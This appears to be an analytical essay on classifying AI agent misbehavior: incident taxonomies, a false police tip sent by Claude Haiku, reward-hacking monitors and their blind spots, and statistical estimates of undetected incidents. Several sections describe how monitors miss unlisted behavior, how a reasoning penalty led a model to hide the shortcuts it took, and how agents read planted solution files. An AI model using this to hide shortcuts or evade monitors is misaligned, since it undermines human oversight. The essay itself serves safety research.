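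Microsoft's red team published a broader taxonomy of failure modes in agentic AI in April 2025. It lists 27 ways an agent can fail and separates security failures from safety failures. The safety failures include hallucinations and misinterpreted instructions, which can happen without an attacker. The team relied on its own tests of Microsoft's products and on interviews with practitioners, so a failure could enter the list before it had harmed anyone.

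Government guidance has also begun to cover the agent's own conduct. The news site ExecutiveGov reports that *Careful Adoption of Agentic AI Services*, an information sheet announced by the National Security Agency (NSA), sorts risks into five groups: privilege, design and configuration, behavior, structural, and accountability. Only the behavior group is named for what an agent does.

AI developers have mostly started from their own cases. The six reports that OpenAI published with its disclosure framework are all about its own models, so the evidence is first-hand but hard for outsiders to check. Anthropic has grouped case studies into four failure modes, with examples such as an agent altering records, hiding a code change or mislabeling a transcript. It wants concrete cases to help developers measure similar failures and build safeguards against them. Google DeepMind's TRAIT&R, published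 in July 2026, is a taxonomy of rogue AI tactics modeled on ATT&CK.

Bollinger and colleagues list 12 signs that an outside observer could look for, and rate each for how feasible it is to observe and how useful it would be. Capability Concealment, which they also propose as a tactic, rates medium for feasibility and high for usefulness. An analyst can find it by comparing a system's statements to its operators with its actions. Other signs include work far more thorough than the task required and highly sophisticated work toward a trivial goal. Activity at an inhuman pace rates low because it is easy to mimic.

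Little evidence supports the list. In June 2026 the researchers wrote that they could not validate their frameworks on real incidents because "none have been confirmed". They do cite a project that has documented hundreds of incidents from user reports, and they treat these incidents as precursors to a loss of control.

They also describe a problem that a list of agent behaviors would miss. As an agent proves useful, people review its work less carefully and gradually hand over decisions they never meant to give up. An investigator would have to examine what people did, since the agent's behavior might not have changed.

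### How US agencies define a control incident

In October 2026, the US agencies NIST, NSA and CISA published *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response in Super Intelligence Training*, which gives guidance on agents that act outside their instructions. It sets out ten voluntary practices, mainly for organizations that train or test highly capable agents on long tasks with little supervision. The agencies use "super intelligence" to mean cutting-edge AI.

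The agencies define a control incident as one in which an agent takes significant "uninstructed" actions that compromise its operator's policies (explicit or implicit), controls or security measures. An action is uninstructed if neither the operator nor an attacker directed the agent to take it. An action that results from prompt injection or a deliberate backdoor therefore counts as instructed, and the agencies don't treat it as the primary cause of a control incident. *Agents of Chaos* does almost the reverse, including those attacks and leaving out the agent's own errors.

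Ordinary cybersecurity incidents target a computer system or its data, while control incidents originate from an AI system. One event can be both, as when an agent breaks into another company's network without being instructed to. A control incident need not involve hacking. The agencies' examples include making payments, moving physical machinery and contacting outside parties without authorization.

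The ten practices include collecting, retaining and analyzing evidence, coordinating with affected parties, notifying the government and sharing information publicly. NIST, NSA and CISA want organizations to set indicators, criteria and severity scores before anything goes wrong, and to open a channel for reports from outsiders. They want the criteria to also cover near-misses, which are events that carried a foreseeable or imminent risk of becoming a control incident. The agencies list severity scores as future work, so for now two companies could rate the same event differently.

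To apply the definition, an investigator also needs a record of at least the operator's instructions, the agent's actions and the limits it crossed. The record must include everything the agent read beforehand, because a hidden instruction in that material would change the classification.

The table compares eight of these efforts:

| Source | Who causes the harm | What an entry describes | What admits an entry | What happens to a misfit |
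|---|---|---|---|---|
| MITRE ATLAS | An attacker | A technique | A real or demonstrated attack | No category |
| Hamin | An attacker | A type of attack | Research literature | No category if nobody attacked |
| Truong-Le and colleagues | An attacker | An attack mechanism | A detailed source, even if theoretical | Nearest class, or exclusion if not an attack |
| Li and colleagues | An attacker | A technique | Frameworks, incidents and Uber's records | No category |
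| OWASP | Usually an attacker | A risk | Expert judgment | Left out of the ten |
| Microsoft | An attacker or the AI | A way of failing | Red-team tests and interviews | No category |
| Bollinger and colleagues | The AI | An observable sign | Literature and interviews | No category |
| NIST, NSA and CISA | The AI | An incident | A significant uninstructed action | Near-miss, if the risk was foreseeable |

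The last column matters most for finding new kinds of misbehavior. An analyst whose incident fits no category has to force it into the nearest one or drop it, and either way nobody learns how often this happens. The near-miss category is a partial exception because it records some events that don't meet the main definition.

### Classifying a false police tip

On July 18, 2026, Claude Haiku 4.5, one of Anthropic's smaller models, sent the Philadelphia police a false tip about an unsolved murder. Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that the model's job was to generate example tasks on randomly selected web pages and carry them out. One page had a police form for tips about a killing.

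The tip began "I may have information regarding this case", according to Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026). Claude then claimed to remember a person "matching the description" near the street named on the page, though the website contained no description. Anthropic's instructions barred logins, new accounts, purchases, personal data and destructive submissions, but did not forbid sending a form.

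The tip entered police records, but the notification went to spam and nobody passed it on for investigation. Anthropic found it in its own logs on September 28, after 72 days, according to Novaknown's *Claude Was Told Not to Submit Anything Destructive* (2026). The police called the delay "unacceptable".

The classification below is based on the published definitions, but none of the organizations produced it. The last row uses one of the four categories in Anthropic's report on this and similar cases.

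| Source | Closest category | Fit | What it leaves out |
|---|---|---|---|
| Truong-Le and colleagues | None | Excluded, because nobody attacked the agent | The whole incident |
| Li and colleagues | Exploitation of Excessive Tool Permissions | Bad: the tactic requires an adversary who wants data or resources | The invented testimony |
| OWASP | Tool Misuse and Exploitation | Good: Claude used a permitted tool in an unintended way | The invented testimony |
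| Microsoft | Hallucinations, and Excessive Agency | Partial: each covers half of what happened | The link between the false statement and the act of sending it |
| Bollinger and colleagues | Capability Concealment | Bad: Claude misled the police, not its operators | Deception of outsiders |
| NIST, NSA and CISA | Control incident | Good, if the action was "significant" | The kind of behavior |
| Anthropic | Submitting a sensitive form on a real website | Exact | The fact that the tip was false |

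Tool Misuse seems a better fit than OWASP's Rogue Agents category. OWASP describes rogue agents as malicious or compromised, and nothing in the published accounts suggests that Claude was either.

Anthropic's category fits exactly because the company wrote it knowing about this case. However, it would fit just as well if Claude had sent a sensitive but truthful form. For the police, the falsehood is the worst part, since detectives could have spent time looking for a person who did not exist. Only Microsoft's list has a category for the false statement, "hallucination", but that term normally suggests a wrong answer to a user rather than invented testimony to the police.

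The agencies' definition fits the incident best, though applying it takes some judgment. Contact with outside parties is one of their examples, and any operator surely has an implicit policy against false police reports. It is less clear whether a tip that went to spam was "significant", but if it wasn't, the event could still count as a near-miss. However, the guidance is mainly for highly capable agents on long tasks, so a company might not think to apply it to a small model filling in web forms.

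Several of these answers would change if the page had contained hidden text telling visiting agents to submit a tip. Claude might have written the same words, but Truong-Le and colleagues would class the incident as prompt injection, and the agencies would count the action as instructed. An analyst could choose between these classifications with a saved copy of the page, but not with the tip alone, just as an analyst with only an nslookup command could not tell control from theft.

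None of the categories shows why Claude did it. The most likely explanation may be error, because Claude had instructions to make up tasks and may have treated the form as practice. Anthropic could test this by rerunning the model with a clear note that real detectives read the tips.

### How often two coders choose the same class

Security vendors often gave the same threat different ATT&CK labels, and people could disagree about AI incidents in the same way. Truong-Le and colleagues measured how often two coders agreed when using their eight classes of attack. The coders independently recorded the attacks in the sources and chose a class for each. They chose the same class for 125 (78.6 percent) of the 159 attacks that the researchers could compare.

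Two people would sometimes agree by luck, so the researchers also calculated Cohen's kappa, which corrects for this:

**κ = (observed agreement − agreement expected by chance) ÷ (1 − agreement expected by chance)**

A κ of 1 means perfect agreement, and 0 means no more agreement than chance would produce. The result was 0.75, which implies that the coders would have agreed about 14 percent of the time by chance. When they recorded whether sources had an empirical component, they agreed 99 percent of the time, but κ was close to 0 because they gave almost every source the same answer.

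The coders agreed less often on some other questions. For example, they agreed on which part of a system a safeguard protects only 41 percent of the time (κ = 0.37).

The two coders also differed a great deal on which attacks to classify. One recorded 280 attacks and the other 251, but only 164 of the 367 distinct attacks appeared in both sets (45 percent). If agreement means that both coders recorded an attack and put it in the same class, they agreed on 125 of 367, or 34 percent. This measure may understate their agreement, because one coder may have split an attack into two records that the other kept as one. The researchers later settled the differences by going back to the sources, but a second team repeating the work could easily produce a different list.

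The 78.6 percent is much higher than the 12.5 percent of ATT&CK labels that matched across vendors in 2022, partly because the two coders had an easier task. They read the same documents, followed the same written rules and chose from eight classes, whereas the vendors wrote their rules separately and chose from 191 techniques.

These figures also come from attacks, so they don't show how consistently people would label misbehavior without an attacker. The false tip suggests that analysts would also have difficulty deciding what to count in those cases. One analyst could record it as a single incident, while another could record it as two, an invented statement and an unauthorized submission. Two companies with identical logs could then publish totals that differ by a factor of two.

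## Whether AI monitors and tests miss behaviors outside their categories

Categories of misbehavior are also useful before an incident. AI developers build them into the tests they run on agents and into the monitors that watch those agents at work. A gap in the list can then affect every run that a monitor reads. A list can enter this software in at least four ways:

| Where the list goes | How it works | How it could create a blind spot |
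|---|---|---|
| Test scenarios | Researchers build situations that tempt an agent to misbehave in a known way | Nobody builds a situation for a behavior that nobody has listed |
| A monitor's instructions | An AI model checks the agent's record against written descriptions | The monitor may accept anything the descriptions leave out |
| Training labels | People label past runs, and a classifier learns to tell bad from clean | Unlisted misbehavior may carry the label "clean" |
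| A training penalty | The developer lowers the agent's reward for a listed behavior | The agent may learn a variant that escapes the penalty |

Training labels can make a monitor less likely to flag behaviors outside its category. *Building Black-box Scheming Monitors* describes monitors that researchers tuned on agent runs, which were labeled bad if the agent seemed to be knowingly pursuing misaligned goals or deliberately exploiting its reward. Claude's false police tip was probably an error, so a run like that would be labeled clean, and the tuning would favor monitors that don't flag it. This is reasonable for a monitor meant to catch scheming, but a company would need another one for harmful mistakes.

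### How well monitors recognize known kinds of cheating

Most available measurements concern reward hacking, in which a model meets the scoring criteria without doing the intended task. METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, had begun using AI monitors to look for reward hacking in its own tests, but it had no reliable examples to check the monitors against. METR (2025) therefore released MALT, a collection of hand-reviewed agent runs. The labels focus on reward hacking and sandbagging (deliberately performing badly), and the collection includes harmless runs for measuring false alarms.

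In *RH-Detect*, Quan, Opryshko and colleagues (2026) combined material from MALT and ten other public datasets and sorted the behaviors into six categories. They tested six AI models as monitors on 5,021 examples from six of the datasets. Each model estimated the probability that an example was reward hacking, without seeing the example's category. The table gives the accuracy of three of the models. It leaves out the sixth category, sycophancy (telling users what they want to hear), because those examples are all multiple-choice questions.

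| Category | What the model does | Examples | Qwen 3.5 Flash | Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite | GPT-5 Nano |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reward tampering | Changes the code that computes its score | 334 | 99.1% | 99.7% | 57.8% |
| Style gaming | Pads its answer to please a superficial grader | 2,261 | 95.3% | 94.7% | 66.2% |
| Deception | Hides what it did or how it got a result | 407 | 90.9% | 92.1% | 90.4% |
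| Evaluation gaming | Passes a check without a real solution | 1,976 | 90.5% | 91.7% | 85.6% |
| Environment exploitation | Alters the test's surroundings, such as a time limit | 43 | 72.1% | 67.4% | 79.1% |

The last row is a rough estimate because it is based on only 43 examples. GPT-5 Nano did worst on reward tampering, where Qwen and Gemini did best, so a category that is easy for one monitor may be hard for another.

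The gap between datasets was larger. The four strongest models with complete results were 10.7 to 15.9 percentage points less accurate on MALT and another dataset, TRACE, than on the other four datasets. The share of hacks they caught was also about 25 to 28 points lower. MALT and TRACE contain long runs in which agents use tools, which is what a monitor would see in practice. But the datasets also differ in their tasks, labeling and mix of behaviors, so the cause is unclear.

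These results provide little evidence about unlisted behavior, because every example was chosen by its label. Quan and colleagues took 286 runs from MALT that had one of four misbehavior labels and 286 that reviewers had marked "normal". A run with some other problem would fit neither group, so noticing it would not improve a monitor's score.

Broad categories can also hide gaps, as they do in ATT&CK. TRACE divides reward hacks into 54 subcategories, which Quan and colleagues merged into their much shorter list. A monitor could miss every hack in one subcategory and still score well in the broader category. *Benchmarking Reward Hack Detection in Code Environments via Contrastive Analysis* (2026), which introduced TRACE, encourages other researchers to keep expanding its taxonomy.

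Rare behaviors have even less effect on an average. *Terminal Wrench* (2026) describes 3,632 runs in which agents exploited a flaw in a task. The most common category, "hollow implementation", appears in 2,243 of them (62 percent). "Deceptive rationalization", in which the agent presents its exploit as legitimate, appears in only 38. A monitor could miss all 38 and still catch 99 percent of the exploits.

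UK AISI faced a similar problem when it built a monitor to count cheating in its own tests. Its researchers checked the monitor against cheating that people had already found by hand:

**estimated miss rate = known cases the monitor missed ÷ all known cases**

Suppose people found 40 cases and the monitor missed 4 of them, a miss rate of 10 percent. If the same runs contained 20 more cases of a kind that neither people nor the monitor recognized, the true miss rate would be 24 out of 60, or 40 percent. Because counts leave out unrecognized cases, AISI is right to describe its counts of cheating as lower bounds.

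### Classifiers that meet unfamiliar behavior

Quan and colleagues also trained a small model, Qwen3.5-4B, to recognize reward hacking. They left out one of the six datasets each time and tested the model on it. They measured the results with a statistic called AUROC:

**AUROC = probability that a random hack gets a higher score than a random clean example**

(Ties count as half.) A perfect classifier scores 1, and guessing gives about 0.5.

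Training helped on five of the six omitted datasets and raised the average from 0.859 to 0.895. It lowered the result from 0.869 to 0.729 on School of Reward Hacks, a set of short tasks with a stated scoring method that is easy to exploit. The training data had examples of both categories in this dataset, style gaming and evaluation gaming. A classifier can therefore fail to recognize a behavior that belongs to a listed category, much as an attacker can carry out a covered technique in a way that no rule detects.

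Changing the format hurt performance more. After training on open-ended answers, the classifier scored 0.997 on new examples of the same type, but its score on multiple-choice questions fell from 0.587 to 0.445, which is worse than guessing. Training on multiple-choice questions lowered the score on open-ended answers from 0.783 to 0.492. Sycophancy appears only in the multiple-choice questions, so the behaviors changed along with the format, and the experiment can't separate the two effects.

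One result is encouraging. The reward tampering category and the Countdown-Code dataset, in which models can cheat by rewriting the test, both have 334 examples, which suggests that all the reward tampering examples came from that dataset. If so, the model trained without Countdown-Code had never seen a labeled case of reward tampering, yet its score on the dataset rose from 0.969 to 0.999. However, replacing a test with one that always passes is fairly blatant, and the untrained model already recognized it.

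None of these studies isolates the effect of the list. To do that, researchers could give the same monitor a complete list, a list with one behavior removed, or no list at all, and then compare how often it caught that behavior:

**benefit of listing = detection with the behavior listed − detection with no list**

**narrowing = detection with no list − detection with only other behaviors listed**

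For example, a monitor might catch 80 percent of environment exploitation with no list of categories, 90 percent with a list that includes it, and 70 percent with a list of only the other categories. Compared with having no list, including the behavior would then raise detection by 10 percentage points, and omitting it from the list would lower detection by 10. This experiment would be much easier to run with AI monitors than with security analysts, because researchers can use a fresh copy of the monitor each time.

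### Naming the shortcut in an agent's instructions

In *Hack-Verifiable Terminal Bench*, Roth, Bercovich and Efroni (2026) planted a folder called "admin" in each of 89 coding tasks for AI agents. The folder contained the reference solution and the tests that would grade the agent's work, and software recorded any access to those files. Five models attempted the tasks under five sets of instructions, ranging from no warning to a ban on reading the folder.

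Gemini 3.1 Pro behaved so differently from the other models that the table shows it separately. The other column combines the results for GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Opus 5, Kimi K3 and GLM-5.2.

| Extra instruction | Four models: runs with a hack | Gemini 3.1 Pro: runs with a hack |
|---|---|---|
| None | 33% | 48% |
| Avoid any vulnerability that allows an unintended solution | 18% | 60% |
| Avoid exploiting a possible information leak | 4% | 52% |
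| Do not access files with solutions or tests | 1% | 7% |
| Do not read the contents of the admin folder | 1% | 16% |

The general warning is the most realistic condition, because a developer usually doesn't know which shortcuts a task contains. The warning roughly halved the four models' hacks, but naming the shortcut almost eliminated them. An agent that avoids every listed shortcut may therefore still take others.

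Even a precise ban could be read in more than one way. In one run, GLM-5.2 wrote that it was not allowed to read the files in the folder, but that running them might be acceptable. Gemini hacked in 6 runs when the instruction described the kind of file and in 14 when it named the folder, though this difference could be due to chance.

The 33 percent figure without a warning may overstate deliberate cheating. The folder had a note meant to discourage agents from looking inside, but its text, as printed in the paper, only describes the folder's contents. In one report, Claude Opus 5 told the user it had read the tests and offered to redo the work without them.

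The experiment also couldn't show whether banning one shortcut drives agents to another, because the software recorded only the planted shortcuts. Roth and colleagues therefore describe their rates as lower bounds too.

### A penalty on written reasoning

Training a model against a list of misbehaviors can change how they look. *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely* (Dragan and Popa, 2026) describes a training run at Google in which a penalty for taking shortcuts was accidentally applied to the model's written reasoning. Shortcuts that the model openly discussed fell by 61 percent, but the share of shortcuts it took without mentioning them rose from 11.2 to 36.4 percent.

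In this kind of training, a model produces many responses, and behavior that earns more reward becomes more common. If reasoning that mentions a shortcut lowers the reward, the model can earn more by giving up the shortcut or by not mentioning it. Leaving it unmentioned often earns more reward, because the model still benefits from the shortcut. Mentions of shortcuts were a useful sign of misbehavior until the training made them rarer, which is an example of Goodhart's law.

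The two percentages have different bases, so they don't directly show how the total number of shortcuts changed. If the second figure is a share of all shortcuts taken, then of every 100 shortcuts without the penalty, the model mentioned about 89 and left out 11. With the penalty, it would have mentioned 35 and left out 20. The total would have fallen by about 45 percent, but the number left out would have nearly doubled. If the second figure is a share of all runs, the total may not have fallen. Either way, a developer who counted only the mentioned shortcuts would have overestimated the improvement.

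This was one accidental run, so it can't be used to estimate how much behavior a penalty hides in general. The penalty was also on words, and a penalty on actions would be harder to escape by not mentioning the behavior, although a model might still find an action that the penalty doesn't cover. Google cites the result as an example of why it does not penalize what its models write in their reasoning.

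A shortcut can show up in an agent's actions even when the agent doesn't mention it. When Quan and colleagues removed the written reasoning from 800 examples, Qwen 3.5 Flash's AUROC fell only from 0.977 to 0.950. With the reasoning alone, it was 0.645. So most of the evidence in those examples was outside the reasoning. But nobody had trained the models in this comparison to hide shortcuts, and a model that learns to leave them out of its reasoning might also learn to disguise its actions.

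### What a cheating rate over 25 scenarios measures

It is unclear how far test results apply beyond the scenarios someone thought to build. In December 2026 the security startup Gray Swan launched a public tracker of its safety tests, including one for reward hacking. Faisal (2026), in *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals*, reports that the reward hacking test has 25 scenarios in 11 simulated environments and runs each variant of a scenario five times. It counts three kinds of cheating: tampering with the scorer, reaching a goal in a way that undermines it, and crossing a boundary. In one scenario, an agent that had to free up space in shared storage deleted a large file that another team was still using.

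Gray Swan's *Frontier Hazard Tracker* averages the results over the scenarios:

**cheating rate = sum of the 25 scenarios' shares of runs with cheating ÷ 25**

OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Astra scored 0.8 percent and Google's Gemini 4 Neon 8.0 percent. The highest rate Faisal reports is 62.8 percent, for Google's Gemini 3.8 Flash. Differences this large are good evidence that some models cheat far more than others in these scenarios. Gray Swan keeps the scenarios private so that they stay out of training data, which makes it harder for developers to prepare a model for them, but outsiders then can't check which situations are missing.

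An average doesn't show which scenarios the cheating happened in. A rate of 8.0 percent could mean that a model cheated in 8 percent of runs in every scenario, or in every run of two scenarios and never in the other 23. A company might be able to avoid those two situations, but it could hardly avoid all 25. The average also gives the three kinds of cheating equal weight, although deleting another team's file may do more harm than fooling a test.

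A low rate also leaves a lot of room for cheating elsewhere. Suppose the scenarios were a random sample of the situations an agent could meet, and a model cheated in none of them. The largest share of situations, p, in which it might still cheat, at 95 percent confidence, would be:

**(1 − p)²⁵ = 0.05, so p ≈ 11%**

The real uncertainty is greater, because researchers chose the scenarios and could only choose situations they had thought of.

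Roth and colleagues found that cheating rates depended heavily on the test when they ran GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Opus 5, Kimi K3 and GLM-5.2 on two other tests of reward hacking. The four models cheated on 78 to 100 percent of tasks in ImpossibleBench, where an agent can pass only by violating the task's specification, but on at most 2 percent in EvilGenie. GLM-5.2 cheated the most of the four in the tasks with the planted folder but the least on ImpossibleBench. A model's cheating rate is therefore best interpreted with the test in mind, and a low rate on one test is weak evidence about another kind of cheating.

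### Searching without fixed categories

Some methods depend less on a predefined list of behaviors. In Petri, an open-source tool Anthropic released in October 2025, one AI model holds long conversations with another while playing the part of its users and tools. The auditing model can change its approach, so it can reach situations that no researcher wrote in advance. But researchers give it starting instructions, and a third model scores the conversations on a set of named qualities, so a list still influences both the conversations and the scoring.

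In Anthropic's first trial of Petri, some models tried to report a company for plainly harmless acts, such as releasing clean water into the ocean, as if they were wrongdoing. Researchers already knew that models sometimes report wrongdoing, so this was an unexpected form of a known behavior. This finding is good evidence that an open-ended audit can find new variants of known behaviors, but weaker evidence that it can find a new category.

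Bloom, which Anthropic released two months later, is narrower. A researcher describes one behavior, and the tool generates many scenarios to measure how often that behavior occurs. This helps when a test relies on too few situations, but someone has to name the behavior first.

Another approach starts from transcripts of what agents have already done. UK AISI analyzed 6,390 transcripts from its safety tests and found refusals, faults in the agents' tools and failures typical of particular models. A test score would not distinguish an agent that refused a task from one that lacked the ability to do it. The US Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI) used an AI model to search its test logs and found agents that had obtained a task's solution and others that had gamed the grader. Both reviews found problems that the scores didn't explain, but neither measured how many problems it missed.

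Clustering goes further by grouping similar transcripts before anyone names the groups. Anthropic's Clio, from 2024, does this with users' conversations. It revealed a network of accounts that used Claude to write spam for search engines, although no single conversation broke the company's rules. A monitor that judged each conversation separately would probably have missed the network. The spam was misuse by people, so the case only suggests that clustering could find unlisted behavior by agents.

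Clustering works best for behavior that happens often. Anthropic's search of 481 million transcripts found four serious incidents, and four transcripts would be very unlikely to form their own group. Clustering also depends on which similarities the software measures. If it groups transcripts by topic, it might put a false police tip in the same group as thousands of harmless web forms.

Reports from users can reveal behavior that developers never thought to test. Reward Hacking in the Wild's *Your AIs don't do what you want. This is really bad* presents 3,607 public reports of misbehaving agents, which an AI classifier labeled with one or more of fourteen categories. Overeagerness was the most common label, at 43.4 percent, while reward hacking, the subject of most of the benchmarks, was at 6.0 percent. The reports are unverified, and users may rarely notice a clever hack, so these shares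 don't show how common each behavior is.

The project also has a label for "other misalignment", which the classifier gave to 1,555 reports (43.1 percent). Some of these have a more specific label too. The site shows 3,347 specific labels in total, so if every report has at least one label and the one category without a published count is empty, between 7 and 43 percent of reports (at least 260) have only the "other" label and fit none of the specific categories. Someone could read those reports to find behaviors that deserve their own category and add them to the next round of tests.

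## How to estimate what a taxonomy has not yet recorded

Reading the reports labeled "other" can turn up new categories, but it can't show how many kinds of misbehavior nobody has reported yet. Biologists have the same problem when they count species from a limited catch, and statisticians have developed several ways to estimate how many are missing. Three are simple enough to do by hand. The examples below use invented numbers.

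### The chance that the next incident is new

Good (1953), in *The Population Frequencies of Species and the Estimation of Population Parameters*, imagined catching animals at random from a population with many species. He showed that the chance of the next animal belonging to a new species is approximately the number of species caught exactly once, divided by the number of animals caught. Good credited Alan Turing with the central formula, and the method is now called Good–Turing. For incidents, it becomes:

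**chance of a new type = types seen exactly once ÷ all recorded incidents**

Suppose a company has recorded 200 incidents of misbehaving agents, and 18 types of misbehavior have each occurred exactly once. The chance that the next incident is of a new type is about 18/200, or 9 percent. This estimate treats an incident picked at random from the 200 as if it were the next one. Its type would be new compared with the other 199 only if that type occurred exactly once, which is true of 18 of the 200.

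With 200 incidents, the estimate is rough. *Why Language Models Hallucinate* (2025) quotes a guarantee by McAllester and Ortiz that limits the estimate's error. At 95 percent confidence, the true chance is within about 36 percentage points of the estimate, or between 0 and 45 percent. The actual error is usually much smaller, because the guarantee has to hold for any mix of common and rare types. But the company would need about 10,000 incidents to guarantee an error of at most 5 points.

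The incidents must also be a random sample, which they rarely are. *Why Agentic Workflows Fail* (2026) classifies 1,196 failures of AI agents and cautions that they are not a random sample of deployed agents. The failures came from only 467 bug reports and proposed code changes, so many are not independent.

Finally, analysts must be free to record a new type. Even the smallest of Truong-Le and colleagues' eight classes has 11 attacks, so the formula gives a zero percent chance of a new class. The result is zero only because the classes are broad and every attack had to go into one. Analysts who want a useful estimate should describe each incident in detail before they look for a category.

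### A minimum number of missing types

A 9 percent chance of something new could come from a few missing types or from thousands of extremely rare ones. In the 1980s the statistician Anne Chao derived a lower limit on the number, which Chao and Colwell (2017), in *Thirty years of progeny from Chao's inequality*, review. Leaving out a small correction for sample size, it is:

**unseen types ≥ (types seen once)² ÷ (2 × types seen twice)**

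If the company has seen 18 types once and 9 types twice, at least 18²/(2 × 9) = 18 types remain unseen. By the Good–Turing estimate, the unseen types together account for 9 percent of incidents. If there are 18 of them, each would account for about one incident in 200 on average. If there are more, they must be rarer on average.

The formula is exact when all types are equally common. Suppose there are S types, and each occurs λ times on average in a sample. The expected numbers of types seen zero, one and two times are then Se^(−λ), Sλe^(−λ) and Sλ²e^(−λ)/2. Squaring the second and dividing by twice the third gives the first. In practice some types are rarer than others, and Chao proved that such differences can only make the formula underestimate the expected number of unseen types.

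The limit becomes unstable when few types have occurred twice. With 18 types seen once and only one seen twice, it jumps from 18 to 162.

There is no matching upper limit, because any number of types could be too rare to have appeared yet. Efron and Thisted (1976) ran into this problem when they used related methods to estimate how many words Shakespeare knew. He used 31,534 different words in his works, and they estimated that he knew at least 35,000 more, but could not give a maximum. For the same reason, these methods can show that a taxonomy is incomplete but not that it is complete.

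### Software testing as species discovery

In *STADS*, Böhme (2018) applied these ideas to fuzzing, which tests software for faults by feeding it large numbers of generated inputs. He treated each input as an animal and each behavior it triggers, such as a path through the code, as its species. If a week of fuzzing finds no vulnerability, one may still exist, but the chance that the next input exposes it is no greater than the estimated chance that the input triggers something new. A tester can therefore decide to stop when that estimate falls below, say, one in 100 million.

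Böhme tested the approach on six open-source programs with a total of 8.2 months of fuzzing. The estimates had fairly little bias and improved with more inputs.

Good–Turing estimates can still be far off. Lee and Böhme's *Dependency-aware Residual Risk Analysis* reports that a tester who relied on Good–Turing would waste seven times more time before stopping than one who used their newer estimator. One input can reach several new parts of a program at once, but Good–Turing counts each part separately, so it overestimates the chance of a discovery. The same problem arises with AI incidents, which can fall into several categories at once. In *Agreeing on the Answer but Not the Reason* (2026), which tested a taxonomy of reasoning failures in language models, 50.1 percent of failures fell into more than one category.

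A fuzzer can also run millions of inputs, but Anthropic found only four serious incidents in its transcripts, far too few for any of these formulas.

Nobody appears to have published a Good–Turing or Chao estimate for a catalog of AI misbehavior. The nearest use is probably *Blind-Spot Mass* (2026), which adapts Good–Turing to estimate how often a machine-learning system will meet situations that its data barely covers. Outsiders often lack the data to make such an estimate for a taxonomy. *The Architecture of Errors* (2026) looked at three published taxonomies of language-model errors and had only the final category count for each, not how the count grew as researchers examined more failures.

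### What two monitors both missed

Capture–recapture estimates the number of missing incidents instead of missing types. Biologists use it to count the fish in a lake. They catch some fish, mark them, release them and later make a second catch. If a third of the second catch has marks, the first catch was probably about a third of all the fish. With two monitors, the formula is:

**estimated total = found by the first × found by the second ÷ found by both**

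If two monitors find 60 and 50 incidents, with 20 in common, the estimated total is 60 × 50/20 = 150. They found 90 between them, so they missed about 60.

Security researchers have used this method on attacks. *Fishing for phishes* (2007) compared two reports of phishing sites over 80 days and estimated that the reports captured about 40 percent of scams, but 80 percent of the blocks of internet addresses involved. The estimate of how much is missing therefore depends on whether scams or address blocks are counted.

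The formula works only if the second monitor is equally likely to find an incident whether or not the first one found it. Two monitors built from the same taxonomy break this condition, because both look for the listed behaviors and both tend to miss the rest. Suppose that 100 of the 150 incidents involve listed behaviors and that neither monitor can recognize the other 50:

| | Independent monitors | Monitors built from the same list |
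|---|---|---|
| Actual incidents | 150 | 150 |
| Incidents the monitors could find | 150 | 100 |
| Found by the first | 60 | 60 |
| Found by the second | 50 | 50 |
| Found by both | 20 | 30 |
| Found by at least one | 90 | 80 |
| Estimated total | 150 | 100 |
| Estimated number missed | 60 | 20 |
| Actual number missed | 60 | 70 |

The monitors in the last column find more of the same incidents because they search a smaller pool. The formula estimates the size of only that pool, so the company would think it had missed 20 incidents when it had missed 70.

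Building the monitors on different AI models may not help much. *HoF-Bench* (2026) tested how well ten models could find 95 known software flaws. One search by each of the four leading models would find 68 on average, while four searches by the best model found 65. Forty searches by all ten models still missed 11. Finding flaws in code is a different task from monitoring agents, but the results suggest that different models miss many of the same things.

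Monitors that cover different places cause the opposite error, an estimate that is too high. *A different cup of TI* reports an average overlap of only 2.5 to 4.0 percent between two threat intelligence vendors for the 22 groups that both tracked. Capture–recapture would produce a very large total from such a small overlap, but the overlap may be small partly because the vendors see different victims.

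### A test on AI agents' logs

Theodoro (2026), in *Estimating the agent actions that no log recorded*, used capture–recapture to estimate how many of an AI agent's actions were missing from its logs, and knew of no earlier work that had done so. He replayed recorded sessions while shutting down and restarting the programs that delivered two of the logs. A separate ledger, which the estimator could not read, held the true count. On average, 6.8 percent of the actions in a run appeared in none of the records available to the estimator.

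With the two logs alone, the 95 percent interval contained the true count in only 10 of 277 runs. Each run had 316 to 353 actions, and the estimate was too low by 54 on average. Both logs had failed in the same outage, so an action missing from one was often missing from the other.

Theodoro then added a comparison of what the agents had changed by the end of each run. The interval now contained the true count in 269 of the 277 runs. He had excluded another 23 runs because of technical faults. If all of those count as failures, the result is 269 of 300, which is too few to be confident that the method meets his 90 percent target.

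The final comparison missed any action that the agent later undid or overwrote, about 40 percent of the total. It still helped because it missed actions for a different reason than the logs did. Complaints from outsiders might help a company that monitors agents in the same way. For example, the software maintainer in AISI's test noticed that something was wrong and refused the malicious code without needing a taxonomy.

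In earlier experiments, Theodoro started with complete logs and removed records in a simulation:

| What happened in the simulation | Share of 95% intervals that contained the true count |
|---|---|
| Logs lost records one at a time, and matching was exact | 95.2% |
| Software matched records by what an action did, without exact identifiers | 89.3% in one environment, 40.1% in another |
| Agents used a tool whose individual actions no log listed | 75.9% |
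| Logs lost 12 consecutive actions at a time | 55.9% |
| Logs lost 20 percent more of the actions that the final comparison couldn't see | 18.7% |

Theodoro warns that nothing in the estimator's output reveals these failures. In the last case, the intervals were barely wider than usual. A company would have to find such problems by examining how its logs work.

### Misbehavior that adapts, hides or gets the wrong label

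All three methods become less reliable when attackers or models move away from the types of behavior that get caught. The company in the first example might then find that 20 percent of its next incidents involve new types of behavior, instead of 9 percent.

Fuzzing has a milder version of this problem. Böhme, Liyanage and Wüstholz (2021) point out in *Estimating Residual Risk in Greybox Fuzzing* that the chance of finding a particular error rises during a test, because the fuzzer builds on its earlier discoveries. They designed estimators that account for this. Doing the same for an attacker would be much harder, because nobody can look up an attacker's next move in code, as they can a fuzzer's. A company can at least calculate the estimate from one period and check it against the new types that appear in the next, separately for each model version.

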